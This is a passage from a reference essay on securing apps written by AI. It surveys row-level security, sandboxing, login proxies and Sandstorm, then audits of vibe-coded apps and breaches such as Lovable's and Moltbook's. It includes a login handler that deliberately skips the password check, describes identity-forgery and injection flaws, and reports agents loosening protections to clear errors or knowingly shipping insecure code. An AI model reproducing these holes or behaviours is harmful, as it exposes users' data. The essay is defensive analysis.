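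PostgreSQL never applies the policies to superusers or to accounts with the `BYPASSRLS` attribute, and it normally exempts the table's owner as well. An app that connects with the account that created its tables therefore runs without the protection, unless the owner has chosen to be subject to the policies.

Database views can open another gap. A view in PostgreSQL is a saved query that other queries can use like a table, and by default it reads the underlying data with its creator's rights. If the creator owns the claims table, a view for monthly reports can show Ana everyone's claims. Since version 15, an option lets a view use the caller's rights instead. Tessl, a registry of instructions for AI coding tools, includes this option in its guide to row-level security.

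Other policies allow too much. `USING (true)` admits everyone, and because PostgreSQL combines policies with "or", one such policy overrides the stricter ones beside it. Experts make this mistake too. PostgreSQL's note *Doc* describes a correction to the manual. A sample policy was supposed to let people view all rows and change only their own, but it also let them delete other people's rows or take ownership of them. The maintainers corrected the manuals for every version back to 9.5.

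Policies that read a second table can also leak data because of timing. In an example from the manual, an administrator lowers a user's clearance and writes a new secret in the same transaction. A query the user started just before can read the new secret while still checking the old clearance.

Zhang and colleagues object that row rules silently remove data. If an employee in finance runs the quarterly total under the `own_claims` policy, the database adds up only that employee's claims, and the app presents the result as the company's total. PostgreSQL has a setting for backups that raises an error instead of leaving out rows. Row rules are also less expressive than Blockaid's views. A view can show when colleagues are busy without revealing which meetings they attend, but a rule that shows or hides whole rows or cells cannot.

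A row rule also stops applying to data once the query returns it. Maria may read Ben's hotel bill, so a handler that runs for Maria can fetch it and then email it to the whole sales team. Labels would block the email. *Information-Flow Control for Database-backed Applications* makes the general point that securing the program and the database separately can leave the combination insecure.

### Why the weaker tool spread

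Zhang and colleagues blame the specialised languages and frameworks that most earlier systems required. Parker (2019) mentions two further obstacles: analysing a program before it runs can raise too many false alarms, and checking it as it runs can slow it down. Most of the slowdowns measured in these four systems were small, so speed was probably not their main obstacle.

Row-level security was much easier to adopt. It was already in the database, it worked with any programming language, and a team could try it on one table. It also had permanent maintainers, whereas RESIN changed the PHP interpreter in 103 places, and somebody would have had to carry those changes into each new version. Alibaba Cloud and VMware document nearly identical row rules in their own databases, PolarDB and Greenplum.

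The feature was easy to adopt partly because it was off by default, so existing applications kept working after an upgrade. But new tables also start without protection, so developers can easily leave one exposed by mistake.

### When a model has to learn the framework

AI models can do some of the work that made these systems hard to adopt. Developers who tried Hails asked for better documentation with recipes and for tools to generate routine code, and students working with Jacqueline complained about boilerplate. A model can write boilerplate quickly, and it could restructure a program the size of MoinMoin, saving developers weeks of work. Strict systems may suit a model better than a human beginner, because an error message from Blockaid gives the model something to correct, whereas an empty result from a row rule looks like a normal answer.

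There is little evidence on how well this works. Models are trained on far more Django and SQL than code for research frameworks, so they may make more mistakes with the research frameworks. If an output keeps getting blocked, a model might also fix the error by declassifying the data or loosening the policy, and a user who can't read code would see only that the app now works. This is a reason to keep the policy and the declassifying routines where the model cannot change them without approval.

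RESIN, Jacqueline and Blockaid were designed to guard against careless programmers, not malicious ones. That limit matters more now, because a platform that treats generated code as untrusted needs something closer to Hails. Cloudflare OS, a platform from August 2026, applies a related idea by tracking what an AI agent has read.

A model also can't infer a policy that nobody has stated. It could probably write Spree's 84 views in minutes, but it would need to be told the rules behind them. One rule lets customers still see pictures of a discontinued product if they once bought it, and a different shop might reasonably want the opposite.

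## 2010–2024: Serverless hosting, login proxies and one sandbox per document

Hails and Jacqueline required developers to write their programs in a new way, but hosting companies could leave most of a program unchanged and add protection around it. Cloud providers found ways to run thousands of strangers' programs on one machine without letting them read each other's data. Google put a login check in front of its internal applications, so that requests from unknown people never reached them. Sandstorm, a startup's platform from 2014 that hardly anyone paid for, ran a separate copy of an application for every document and controlled who could open each one. Of these three designs, only Sandstorm's would have stopped Ana from seeing Ben's hotel bill.

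### Strangers on one machine

In *serverless hosting*, a customer uploads code and the provider runs it whenever a request arrives. Most customers' code is idle most of the time, so the provider puts code from many customers on the same machine, where any customer might try to attack the others.

The usual way to keep programs apart is to run each one as a separate process with its own memory. Cloudflare's *Mitigating Spectre and Other Security Threats* (2020) explains why the company rejected this for Workers, its serverless product. Workers makes every customer's code available in all of Cloudflare's locations, about 200 at the time, some with room for only a few machines. Each machine therefore has to hold code from thousands of customers, with a couple of megabytes of memory for each. A single processor core may switch between customers thousands of times a second, and separate processes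 could easily take ten times as much processor time.

Cloudflare instead uses *isolates*, which are compartments inside V8, the engine that runs JavaScript in Google's Chrome browser. Many isolates share one process, and V8 keeps the code in each from reaching the others' memory. As with Java, this protection is only as good as the engine. Cloudflare concedes that V8 is very complicated and gives attackers more to target than a virtual machine does. But Google tests V8 continuously and pays five-figure rewards to people who find ways out of it. V8's developers publish their fixes, so attackers can study them too. Cloudflare gets a fix into production within 24 hours, while Chrome took 15 days in 2020.

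Cloudflare also surrounds the whole process with a second sandbox, in case somebody breaks out of an isolate. This sandbox uses Linux features to block all access to files and the network. An ordinary container can't be this strict, because it has to read the customer's program from disk to start it. The Workers runtime has already started when the block takes effect, and it gets customers' code from a separate *supervisor* process. The runtime can request a program only with an encryption key that arrives with a visitor's request, so an attacker who took over the runtime could not list or fetch every customer's code. Cloudflare also keeps free-plan customers out of the processes that serve large companies.

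*Egress*, the network traffic leaving the sandbox, goes through a proxy that blocks requests to Cloudflare's internal services and labels each request with the program that sent it. But the proxy lets programs contact any public website, so it does little to stop a customer's own faulty code from sending data to the wrong place.

### A clock that stands still

Isolates are vulnerable to *Spectre* attacks even if V8 has no bugs. A modern processor predicts which instructions come next and starts on them early. If the prediction is wrong, it discards the results, but the discarded work still changes which data is in the cache, the processor's fast memory. Spectre attacks make the processor read secret data during this discarded work, then infer the data by timing later reads. Cloudflare acknowledged in 2020 that nobody had fully fixed this, even for virtual machines.

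Cloudflare's defence is to take away the stopwatch:

```js
let start = Date.now();
doSpectreAttack();
let end = Date.now();    // always equal to start
```

According to *Security model*, Cloudflare's current documentation, `Date.now()` in Workers returns the time of the last input or output and does not advance while code runs. Cloudflare also forbids programs to use several threads, because one thread could act as a clock by counting steadily while another carried out the attack. Cloudflare froze the clock in mid-2017, before researchers announced Spectre. A browser could not easily do the same, since existing web pages depend on a working clock.

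Attackers can still measure from outside how long a Worker takes to respond. Internet delays add noise to these measurements, but an attacker can repeat them many times and take an average. Cloudflare and the outside experts it consulted could not build a remote attack that worked in production, though this does not prove that nobody could. The company also moves programs with suspicious performance patterns into their own processes, where the operating system's defences apply. An honest customer's program moved by mistake runs only slightly slower. These measures aim to make an attack too slow to be useful. They depend on Cloudflare accepting only JavaScript and WebAssembly, a portable format for compiled code, because a program written in the processor's own instructions could read the hardware's timer directly.

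### Firecracker and gVisor

Many customers want to run ordinary Linux programs, which isolates cannot run. Containers can, but all containers on a machine share one *kernel*, the core of the operating system, and a bug in it may let one customer take over the machine. A virtual machine gives each customer a separate kernel and uses processor features to keep customers apart, as Amazon Science's *How AWS’s Firecracker virtual machines work* (2020) explains.

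Virtual machines used to be too slow and heavy for code that might run for a fraction of a second. Amazon therefore built Firecracker, which has run customers' code in its Lambda service since 2018. *Firecracker* (Agache, Brooker and colleagues, 2020) describes a deliberately sparse design that does not imitate old hardware and cannot move a running machine to another host. Amazon's cloud division, AWS (2019), reported that each small virtual machine launched in under 125 milliseconds and used under 5 megabytes of memory, not counting what the customer's own software needs.

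Google's gVisor puts a substitute kernel, the *Sentry*, between a program and the host's kernel. When the program asks to open a file, the Sentry handles the request with its own code and never passes it straight to the host. According to gVisor's *Security Model*, the Sentry can use only a restricted set of the host's functions. An attacker would normally need one bug to take over the Sentry and another to get from there into the host. In a security record that runs to 2026, the gVisor project selected high-impact Linux kernel flaws and judged that gVisor defends against 96% of them.

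| Design | What customers on one machine share | Main cost | What it runs |
|---|---|---|---|
| V8 isolates | A process, V8, the host's kernel and the processor | A very complex engine to keep secure | JavaScript and WebAssembly |
| gVisor | The host's kernel, through a restricted set of calls, and the processor | Slower performance for some programs | Most Linux programs |
| Firecracker | The host's virtualisation software and the processor | A kernel to start for each machine | Linux programs |

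gVisor's developers warn against assuming that virtualisation hardware makes a system safer, so the table is not a ranking from weakest to strongest. The software that imitates devices for a virtual machine can also have serious bugs. Researchers disclosed new isolation flaws in hosting platforms in 2026.

None of the three would help Ben, because they separate a hosting company's customers from one another, and he and Ana work for the same customer.

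### Login before the app

Companies traditionally let remote employees into internal applications through a VPN, which connects a computer to the company's network. In *How to use BeyondCorp to ditch your VPN*, Saltonstall (2017) dates Google's move away from VPNs to 2010. Google's replacement, BeyondCorp, checks the person and the device on each request, wherever they are.

The checks happen in an *identity-aware proxy*, a server that receives every request before the application does. *BeyondCorp Part III* (Cittadini, Spear and colleagues, 2016) describes Google's version, which all its internal web services had to use. The proxy identifies the user and the device, and forwards the request only if the company's rules allow it. If the proxy forwards none of a stranger's requests, the stranger can't exploit a bug in the expense app.

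Keeping the rules in one place also helps in an emergency. When attackers could exploit plug-ins in Google's Chrome browser, the security team added a rule that sent anyone with an outdated version to a page of update instructions. The rule took effect across the company within 30 minutes. If each application had done its own checks, every team would have had to make the change.

Google deliberately wrote broad rules, such as "Vendors in group G are allowed access to Web application A." Cittadini and colleagues left the applications to make finer decisions, such as whether a user may modify a particular record. The proxy can therefore verify Ana's identity and confirm that sales staff may use the expense app, but it has no record of who owns claim 417.

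The proxy removes the user's login credential before it forwards a request, so the application cannot use the credential to send further requests in her name. This is a useful precaution if an AI wrote the application. But the application still needs to find out who the user is, so the proxy adds that information in a header, a labelled line that travels with the request. Google sells a similar proxy to its cloud customers. Google Cloud's *Securing your app with signed headers* describes the header, whose main fields for Ana might look like this:

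| Field | Example | What the app should check |
|---|---|---|
| `email` | ana@company.example | Nothing, since this is the answer it needs |
| `iss` | Google's proxy service | That the expected service issued the header |
| `aud` | /projects/1234/apps/expenses | That the header is for this app and not another |
| `exp` | Ten minutes from now | That the header has not expired |

The proxy signs these fields with a private key, and the app can verify the signature with Google's public key. If Ana replaces her address with Ben's, the signature no longer matches.

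### When the app has a second entrance

The app has to verify the signature because a request may reach it without going through the proxy. Someone may have switched the proxy off or misconfigured the firewall, or the request may come from another machine in the same project. Google's proxy also sends the user's email address in a simpler, unsigned header, and it deletes any copy of that header that a visitor supplies. But if Ana can connect to the app's server directly, she can put Ben's address in the header, and an app that relies on it will treat her as Ben.

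Whether this second route exists depends on the hosting. Brave New Geek, a software engineering blog, warns that anyone who can reach the app's port on one of Google's virtual machines can bypass the proxy, but says Google's App Engine hosting doesn't have this problem. Cloudflare's *Application token* requires apps behind its login proxy to verify the signature, unless they connect to Cloudflare through a private tunnel.

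Verifying the signature is not always enough. Amazon's Application Load Balancer distributes traffic among servers and can also log users in. Miggo (2024), a security company, found that an attacker could set up a load balancer in their own Amazon account and use it to get a false identity for somebody else's app, with a genuine Amazon signature. Apps were safe if they checked which load balancer had signed the identity, or if they accepted traffic only from their own load balancer. Amazon added the first precaution to its documentation in May 2024 and the second in July.

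Miggo estimated that more than 15,000 applications were potentially vulnerable. According to SecurityWeek's *Thousands of Apps Using AWS ALB Exposed to Attacks*, Amazon said the true number was much smaller and blamed its customers' configurations. Miggo had counted internet addresses where the login feature appeared to be on, which doesn't show how many of the apps lacked the check or had a second entrance. But AWS's *CVE-2024-8901* and *CVE-2024-10125* (2024) report that two of Amazon's own software packages verified identities without checking the signer, so the check was evidently easy to omit.

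An office manager working with an AI is unlikely to do better than Amazon's programmers. If the generated app has to verify the header, login security again depends on generated code. A platform can avoid this by closing every route to the app except the one through the proxy, or by verifying the header in a layer that the AI can't edit.

### One container for each document

Sandstorm was server software that people could run at home or at work and install apps on, as they would on a phone. Most of the apps were existing open-source programs, such as the text editor Etherpad. LWN, a Linux news site, reported in 2014 that Sandstorm's developers wanted people without technical skills to be able to run it.

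Normally one copy of Etherpad serves everyone and keeps all their documents in one database. Sandstorm instead created a new copy for every document, in a container with its own files and database, and called each copy a *grain*. People logged in to Sandstorm rather than to each app. When someone opened a grain, Sandstorm checked whether they had access, started the container if necessary and passed their requests to it through a proxy.

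Suppose the expense app ran on Sandstorm with one grain for each claim, and its handler still lacked the ownership check. Ana could try to get Ben's hotel bill in several ways:

1. She asks Sandstorm to open Ben's grain. Ben has not shared it with her, so Sandstorm refuses before any of the app's code runs.
2. She opens her own grain and changes the claim number in the request to 417. The faulty handler runs, but the database in this container holds only claim 416.
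3. She installs a malicious version of the app, which tries to contact Ben's grain. Its container has no network connection except a channel to Sandstorm, which won't connect it to a grain that nobody has given her access to.

Etherpad had a flaw of this kind in 2015. A request to export one document also returned every other document whose identifier contained the requested identifier, so an attacker could extract everything on the server by requesting a few very short identifiers. A grain held only one document, and anyone able to send the request could already read it.

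The protection depends on how much goes into each grain. Sandstorm advised developers to make each grain the smallest item that someone might want to share separately. If the expense app kept a whole department's claims in one grain, the handler would again need its ownership check.

Sandstorm could enforce only whether a person had access to a grain. If Ben let Maria read his claim but not change it, Sandstorm would add her permissions to each of her requests and rely on the app to enforce them. If an AI left the permission check out of the editing handler, Maria could change the amount. Before May 2015, Sandstorm did not supply the permissions. Renshaw and Varda (2015) acknowledged that many apps had no access control of their own, so anyone who shared an Etherpad document had to let the recipient edit it.

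When grains had to exchange data, Sandstorm used capabilities. A grain could request a certain kind of resource, and Sandstorm would show the user a list of suitable ones in a window called the *Powerbox*. Choosing a resource also gave the grain permission to use it, just as picking a file to upload to a website gives the site only that file. Sandstorm's example was a forum that notifies its members by email. The forum would receive a capability to write to each member's chosen address but no general ability to send email, so it could not send spam. Producing the finance department's quarterly total would be more awkward, because someone would have to connect the reporting app to every employee's claims.

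### Twenty flaws in five apps

Sandstorm's staff looked up known security flaws in five of its apps and worked out what each would have done on their platform. Laroia (2016), in *Sandstorm's security track record, and what it means for self-hosting*, reported that Sandstorm had "wholly or partly mitigated" 95% of them before anyone disclosed them. The list that Sandstorm published contains 20 flaws in these apps, 19 of them under "mitigated". Some examples:

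| App | Flaw | Effect on Sandstorm |
|---|---|---|
| ShareLaTeX, a document editor | A user can run commands on the server | They control only a document they could already edit |
| Tiny Tiny RSS, a news reader | A user can take over the server | They control only their own news feed |
| WordPress, a blogging program | Attackers can forge login cookies | None, because Sandstorm handles the login |
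| WordPress | Attackers can put scripts in comments | None, because the Sandstorm version had no comments |
| Roundcube, an email program | An email can contain a script that runs when the user opens it | Not blocked |

The 95% figure is generous. Sandstorm avoided the flaw in comments only because it didn't offer comments. Five more of the 19 flaws involved tricking a user's browser into sending a harmful request, which Sandstorm made harder by giving each session a random web address. An attacker who could watch the user's network traffic might still discover that address. The company also chose the apps and judged the results itself, and for WordPress it counted only the more severe flaws. But the evidence is convincing for flaws that could have let one user read or control other people's data, because the container held no one else's data.

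Attackers could still exploit the Roundcube flaw because the malicious email belonged in the mailbox. The email's script could copy the victim's recent mail, but it could not change who had access to the grain, and it stopped working when the victim closed the grain.

Sandstorm also blocked grains from using many Linux kernel functions, and Laroia counted 21 kernel flaws that this had made harmless. Later that year, Varda (2016) reported that the filter had stopped Dirty COW, a bug that let ordinary programs take control of a machine. Sandstorm's list includes two kernel problems that Sandstorm did not block. The engineer who discovered them considered both very hard to exploit.

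### An outside test

In early 2017, the security firm DEVCORE tested a Sandstorm-protected server for Taiwan's Department of Cyber Security. DEVCORE's *Sandstorm Security Review* (2018) reports that the testers found several flaws in the apps but could not use them to threaten the server. This is better evidence than Sandstorm's own list because the testers were independent and were trying to break in.

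They then examined Sandstorm's own code and found four flaws, including one that let a malicious app use up the server's resources and one that let a user make Sandstorm send requests to private parts of the network. A mistake in how Sandstorm read email addresses also let outsiders pass as members of an organisation. Those outsiders could install apps, but according to Varda (2017) they still could not open anyone else's grains.

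The fourth flaw let users obtain some of the server's own files through the backup feature. Sandstorm's developers had given the backup program a list of directories to hide, but they later added two directories to the system and forgot to put them on the list. They fixed this by listing the permitted directories instead, which applies Saltzer and Schroeder's principle of fail-safe defaults. DEVCORE still considered Sandstorm a safe platform and mainly credited its assumption that every app is malicious.

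### Slow starts and few buyers

Sandstorm ran out of money in early 2017. It had sold almost no copies of its business version despite hundreds of trials. Varda (2017) blamed an unfinished product and a team of engineers who had underestimated how hard it is to sell to large companies. Most of the team, including Varda, moved to Cloudflare that March. Volunteers were supposed to carry on the open-source project, but Sandstorm (2020) admitted that hardly anyone outside the company had worked on its core. Varda formally handed the project over to its community in January 2024.

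The design also created extra work for app developers. *Thoughts on Sandstorm*, a user's essay, points out that most web apps have their own login and sharing features, which somebody had to remove or bypass before an app would fit Sandstorm. An AI that writes a new app for such a platform can leave them out.

Developers had also never needed their apps to start quickly, because a normal web server starts once and keeps running, but Sandstorm started an app whenever someone opened a document. The project said on its website that grains often started in under a second and, for certain kinds of app, could add less than a megabyte of memory each. But Varda wrote in 2026 that the approach "didn't work well", because every document could take a long time to open and use hundreds of megabytes.

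Varda also thought Sandstorm had come too early. Each user had a separate copy of an app and could change it without affecting anyone else, but too few people had the skill or patience to do so. Varda argues that AI has removed this obstacle. He made this argument while launching a successor to Sandstorm, so he had a reason to blame the timing and not the idea. His explanation in 2017 had been mostly about sales and an unfinished product. The technical problem was real, though, and his work at Cloudflare gave him a way around it. He became the architect of Workers, whose isolates need only a couple of megabytes each, and in 2026 he used these isolates to run Gadgets, the successor's version of grains.

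## 2025–2026: What went wrong when AI wrote the checks

By 2025 a developer could easily switch on row-level security or put a login proxy in front of an app. Someone with no programming experience is unlikely to know about either, so many vibe-coded apps depended on whatever checks the AI wrote. Researchers audited 200 live apps of this kind and found exploitable flaws in 182. Security researchers also found apps whose databases could have enforced the access rules, but the AI had written the rules badly or left them out.

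### An audit of 200 live apps

Deng, Fan and Meng (2026), in *Understanding the (In)Security of Vibe-Coded Applications*, searched GitHub, where programmers publish code. Vibe-coded projects carry no label, so the researchers looked for traces left by two popular tools. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, creates a folder named `.claude`, and the app builder Lovable puts its name in the page's metadata. The search returned 74,800 projects. The researchers dropped tutorials and very small or very large projects, then kept only those in which an AI had made the first commit (saved version) and at least 90% of all commits and lines of code. That left 9,041 applications, 96% of them for the web. Half had more than 8,254 lines of code, and half went from first to last commit in under nine days, so it's unlikely that anyone read most of the code.

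The researchers randomly picked 200 of the 984 web apps that had a working public address. Two AI agents audited each app twice, with different security instructions each time, and produced 11,150 reports. After merging duplicates and discarding flaws that an AI had not introduced, the researchers had 2,125 candidates. Another agent tried to trigger each one on the live site with a harmless probe, which reduced the list to 1,287. Two of the researchers then independently examined the code and the site, and kept the 1,186 flaws that both considered exploitable.

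Two outside researchers checked for flaws the method had missed by auditing 20 of the apps without seeing the reports, and they found nothing new. The method also found 95.7% of the known vulnerabilities in Juice Shop, an app with a maintained list of them.

Flaws appeared in 91.0% of the apps, and 65.77% of the flaws were rated critical or high. The largest category was *broken access control*, the industry's name for missing or faulty authorization, with 339 flaws in 64% of the apps. About three quarters of these were in server code, like the handler for claim 417. One healthcare provider's app exposed a large amount of customer information this way.

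The sample covers only open-source projects made with two tools, and an app with a public address may have no real users. The study also had no matching group of human-written apps, so it can't show that AI makes more of these mistakes than people do. The missing comparison matters less to platform designers, because their platforms have to run the generated code whether or not a human would have done better.

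### How the checks went missing

Deng and colleagues also read each project's history to find out how the flaws got there. They arrived at eight failure modes:

| Failure mode | What happened | Flaws |
|---|---|---|
| Hidden security rules | The app needed a protection that the user had not asked for | 658 |
| Demo-oriented design | The AI built in a shortcut that was suitable only for a demonstration | 174 |
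| Incomplete change propagation | The AI protected some parts of the app and not others | 110 |
| Function-fix side effects | The AI weakened a protection to make an error go away | 100 |
| User-dependent security | The AI left a necessary step to a user who didn't know about it | 72 |
| Forgotten obligations | The AI noted that a check was unfinished and never came back to it | 50 |
| Hallucination | The code relied on something that doesn't exist, such as an invented library function | 13 |
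| Insecure instructions | The project's instructions asked for something unsafe | 9 |

One of the forgotten obligations was in a login page. Simplified, it worked like this:

```js
app.post("/login", async (req, res) => {
  const user = await findUser(req.body.email);
  // TODO: check the password
  req.login(user);
});
```

In one app, anyone who typed a registered email address was logged in as its owner. In another, the AI wrote a check for new routes but didn't add it to 11 older handlers.

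More than half of the flaws involved hidden security rules. Some of these rules are protections that nearly every app needs, such as storing passwords in scrambled form, and a platform can supply those for everyone. Others are checks that depend on what the app is for.

In the 260 cases of incomplete propagation, function fixes and forgotten obligations, the protection had usually existed somewhere in the project, or the AI had at least noted that it was needed. A model with more security knowledge could still lose track of such a check in a later edit.

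### Better prompts and stronger models

To test whether the AI only needed better instructions, Deng and colleagues chose 70 of the flaws and restored each project to its state just before the mistake. They then asked an agent for the same feature and checked whether the same flaw, or a similar one, came back. The baseline was a short, non-expert prompt to GPT-5.6-Terra, a mid-strength OpenAI model. Each of the other seven setups changed one thing. They made three attempts for each flaw in each setup, for a total of 1,680 runs.

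| Setup | Runs in which the flaw came back |
|---|---|
| Baseline | 25.7% |
| Weaker model | 39.5% |
| Stronger model | 26.2% |
| Prompt asks for well-structured code | 22.9% |
| Prompt asks the agent to review its changes | 23.8% |
| Prompt gives detailed technical instructions | 45.7% |
| Agent has a set of security-hardening instructions | 11.9% |
| Prompt says the code must be ready for production | 11.0% |

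Adding a few words about production to the prompt more than halved the rate. The stronger model did no better than the baseline, and the detailed technical prompt did much worse. The paper suggests that the agent followed that prompt so literally that it had less room for its own judgement. The hardening instructions cut hidden-rule flaws from 24.2% to 9.1% but did not reduce forgotten obligations, although only 21 runs per setup tested for those.

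These rates apply to places where an AI had already written insecure code once, so an ordinary feature is probably safer. But an app has many features, and chance affects each one. In 22% of cases, three identical attempts gave a mixture of safe and unsafe code. In 90 of the 434 runs in which the flaw came back, the agent recognised the danger and delivered the insecure code anyway, often with a warning or with a code comment that an office manager who doesn't read code would never see.

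In *The Effect of Security-Focused Prompts on Reported Findings*, Andročec (2026) tested a longer prompt on whole apps. Two coding agents built apps from 100 specifications, once as written and once with an added paragraph of security requirements, including that users could act only on their own resources. With the paragraph, automated scanners reported about a third fewer problems in both agents' apps.

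It also roughly doubled the number of outside packages that the apps declared, and there were more reports of severe vulnerabilities in those packages. The agents often added login and session code to apps that had no users. Nobody confirmed that the reported problems were exploitable, and the scanners could not determine who owned which record. The experiment therefore provides little evidence about whether the paragraph would have protected Ben's hotel bill.

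Prompts and hardening instructions both rely on the model to be careful. Jha and colleagues surveyed 142 studies of vibe-coding security and found that most proposed defences rely on the model's judgement. They list enforceable limits on what agents can do among the open research problems.

### Attacking AI-written backends

A more direct test is to have a model write a backend, the part of an app that runs on the server, and then attack it. *BaxBench* (Vero, Mündler and colleagues, 2025) does this with 392 tasks, which combine 28 scenarios with 14 web frameworks. It checks that each backend works, then runs attacks that security experts wrote for the scenario. According to the BaxBench project page, even the best model wrote a broken or insecure backend in 62% of the tasks. Across all the models, about half of the working backends were insecure.

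*Applying Security by Design at the Point of Execution* (2026) reports newer scores from three runs of the 28 scenarios in Python frameworks. Without a security reminder, 23 to 26 backends worked in each run, and 16 to 18 of those also withstood the attacks. That is 57% to 64% of the 28 tasks, up from 38% for the best model on the project page. However, the earlier figure covers six programming languages, some of which may be harder.

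The paper also reports tests in which the model received relevant security requirements while it worked. In one run, this raised the share of working backends that were secure from 65% to 86%. But the number of secure, working backends rose only from 17 to 18, because five fewer backends worked.

Wu, Ge and colleagues built *Last Secure Code Benchmark* (2026) from 150 vulnerabilities in real software. They removed the vulnerable part of a program, which ranged from a single function to thousands of lines, and asked an agent to write it again from a description that did not mention security. They then replayed the original attack against the new code. The six agents they tested wrote working code in 73.6% to 91.3% of the tasks. The best, Anthropic's Claude Fable 5, wrote code that was both working and secure in 25.1%.

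That number is low partly because the researchers chose difficult cases in which human programmers had already made the mistake, so it doesn't measure how often everyday AI code is insecure. The differences between types of flaw are more useful here. Across all agents, 34.3% of attempts succeeded where the danger was a memory error, which a careful programmer prevents with a check beside the risky operation. The rate was 18.3% for access control and 0.7% for information exposure, where the code has to withhold certain data, though that 0.7% rests on only eight vulnerabilities. In the last two groups, the right check depends on a policy that the description never stated.

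Adding one sentence to the prompt asking for secure code raised the score of OpenAI's GPT-5.6-Sol from 24.7% to 46.2%. Information exposure remained among the lowest-scoring categories because the prompt still didn't state the policy.

*Coding Agents Propagate Vulnerabilities in Code Bases* (2026) reports no link, in its experiments, between a model's skill at finding or repairing vulnerabilities and the security of the code it writes. This problem may therefore not shrink as models get better at security work.

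### How many of the flaws a platform would remove

The table sorts the 1,186 flaws by what would probably have happened to them if the 200 audited apps had run on a platform that handles login, applies a correct access rule to every request for data and confines the code to a sandbox. The counts come from Deng and colleagues, but the sorting is this reference's own estimate.

| Effect of the platform | Categories, with number of flaws | Share of all flaws | Share of critical and high flaws |
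|---|---|---|---|
| Removed | Broken access control (339), authentication failures (176) | 43% | 50% |
| Contained | Injection (199), data integrity failures (12) | 18% | 19% |
| Left | Cryptographic failures (112), security misconfiguration (108), supply chain failures (73), logging failures (64), insecure design (62), mishandled errors (41) | 39% | 30% |

In an *injection* attack, the app treats text from a visitor as a command. If Ana types SQL into the expense app's search box, a badly written handler may run it. The database would still apply Ana's row rule and return only her own claims, although the platform would not fix the handler. A malicious script that Ana plants in a claim's description is a bigger problem, because it could act with Maria's permissions when Maria opens the claim. Many of the supply chain failures came from exposed secrets or unchanged default passwords, which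 a sandbox does not stop an attacker from using.

The estimate could be much too high or much too low. "Broken access control" covers forgotten ownership checks but also rules specific to one company, such as who may approve a claim. If the platform could handle only half of that category, the share of flaws removed would fall to 29%. Some of the cryptographic failures, though, are secrets that the AI left where visitors could read them, and a platform could keep those out of the generated code. Removing all the cryptographic failures and misconfigurations as well would raise the share to 62%. It's also unclear from the counts how many of the 182 affected apps would have had no flaws left, but probably not many would, since half of them had six or more.

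An experiment would give better evidence than a mapping. Researchers could give a model the same hundred specifications twice, once for an ordinary server and once for a platform that supplies login and data permissions, and then attack both sets of apps. None of the studies above did this. Andročec's comparison of twin apps comes closest, but both versions had their security checks in the generated code.

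The biggest assumption in the table is that the access rule is correct. On several platforms, the AI wrote that too.

### Lovable and the rules nobody checked

Many Lovable apps have no handlers like the one for claim 417. The code in the browser queries the database itself, with a line such as this:

```js
supabase.from("claims").select("*")
```

Supabase hosts PostgreSQL databases and makes them reachable over the web. The request carries a key that anyone can find in the page's code. Supabase intends this, and it is safe as long as row-level security rules limit what someone with the key can do. Without those rules, the line above returns every claim in the company to anyone on the internet.

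Apps built with Lovable often lacked secure rules for who could access which database rows, so an attacker could bypass the app's pages and query its database directly. *Statement on CVE-2025-48757* (Palmer, 2025) dates the discovery of this flaw to 20 March 2025. Some apps had rules, but *CVE-2025-48757* (Palmer, 2025) describes policies that "don't match the business logic". Attackers could read personal data and passwords without logging in, and in some projects could add or change data.

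The problem entered the public catalogue of vulnerabilities that May. *CVE-2025-48757* (2025), a page from INCIBE, Spain's national cybersecurity institute, gives it a severity of 9.3 out of 10. *PT-2025-23236 · Lovable · Lovable* (2025), an entry in the database of the security company Positive Technologies, reports more than 170 exposed apps, though that count is second-hand.

Lovable disputes that this was a vulnerability in its product. According to the US government's entry, NVD's *CVE-2025-48757 Detail*, the company says each customer accepts responsibility for protecting the data in their own app. Only the customer knows which employees should see which claims, but many people use Lovable because they can't write such rules themselves, and they can't check them either. Deng and colleagues call this a mismatch between responsibility and capability. Lovable could also have blocked strangers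 who hadn't logged in from reading a table of personal data by default, since that rule requires no knowledge of the customer's business.

### Moltbook's four repairs

Moltbook, a social network for AI agents, attracted a lot of attention in January 2026. Its founder announced that he "didn't write a single line of code" for it. In *Hacking Moltbook*, the cloud security company Wiz reports that on 31 January its researchers found the site's Supabase key within minutes of browsing. The database had no row-level security, so anyone could read and change every table.

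The tables held login tokens for 1.5 million agents, which belonged to about 17,000 people. An attacker could use a token to take over the agent's account. The tables also held about 35,000 email addresses and thousands of private conversations, some of which contained keys to the participants' OpenAI accounts.

Moltbook's team responded quickly, but it took them four attempts over about three hours:

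| Time (UTC) | What happened |
|---|---|
| 22:06 | Wiz reports the missing rules |
| 23:29 | The team secures the tables of agents, owners and administrators |
| 00:13 | They secure private messages, votes and other tables |
| 00:31 | Wiz finds that it can still edit any post |
| 00:44 | They block the edits |
| 00:50 | Wiz finds more open tables, one with 29,000 email addresses |
| 01:00 | They secure the rest |

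Securing dozens of tables can go wrong in much the same way as adding a check to dozens of handlers.

Wiz researcher Gal Nagli told Fortune (2026) that his team had found the same exposure in many other vibe-coded apps. He gave no count, and Wiz sells products that look for such problems. The Moltbook case is well supported because another researcher, Jameson O'Reilly, independently found the same exposure.

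If Supabase had kept every table closed until someone wrote a rule for it, Moltbook would not have worked at first, and its founder would have noticed. But the AI might then have cleared the error by writing a rule that gave everyone access. The 100 function-fix flaws in Deng and colleagues' study arose in a similar way.

### Apps open to anyone with the link

Some apps had no login at all. RedAccess, an Israeli security company, searched for publicly reachable apps and web pages built with four popular tools. Axios' *AI vibe-coding apps leak sensitive data* (2026) reports that the company found 380,000, about 5,000 of which contained sensitive corporate data. RedAccess gives a lower figure in its own article for The Hacker News (2026). It says that roughly 5,000 looked corporate and that more than 2,000 of those held sensitive data, or about half a percent of everything it found. Some of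 these apps gave administrator access to anyone who opened the link.

RedAccess sells a product for detecting such apps, and outsiders can't easily check its totals. But Axios looked at several of the apps itself and found internal financial information from a Brazilian bank and complete customer-service conversations from a British cabinet supplier. PPC Land reports that RedAccess contacted the apparent owners of a few dozen apps, who confirmed the data was real.

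The companies behind the tools objected. Replit's chief executive, Amjad Masad, said that people can expect a public app to be public, and that users can make an app private with one click. Wix, which owns the app builder Base44, said that RedAccess had withheld the addresses Wix needed to investigate, and that the owners of two of the apps had made them public on purpose.

Masad is right that a public app is not in itself a security flaw. But according to the researchers, some of the tools made apps public by default, and someone who has just built a hospital staff schedule may not think to check the setting. Accidental exposure is the easiest of these failures for a platform to prevent, because it can require a company login for every new app without knowing what the app does, and ask for an explicit decision before making the app public. That would keep strangers out of the expense app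 as long as the platform's own login works, though Base44's once did not.

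## From November 2025: Platforms that supply login and data permissions

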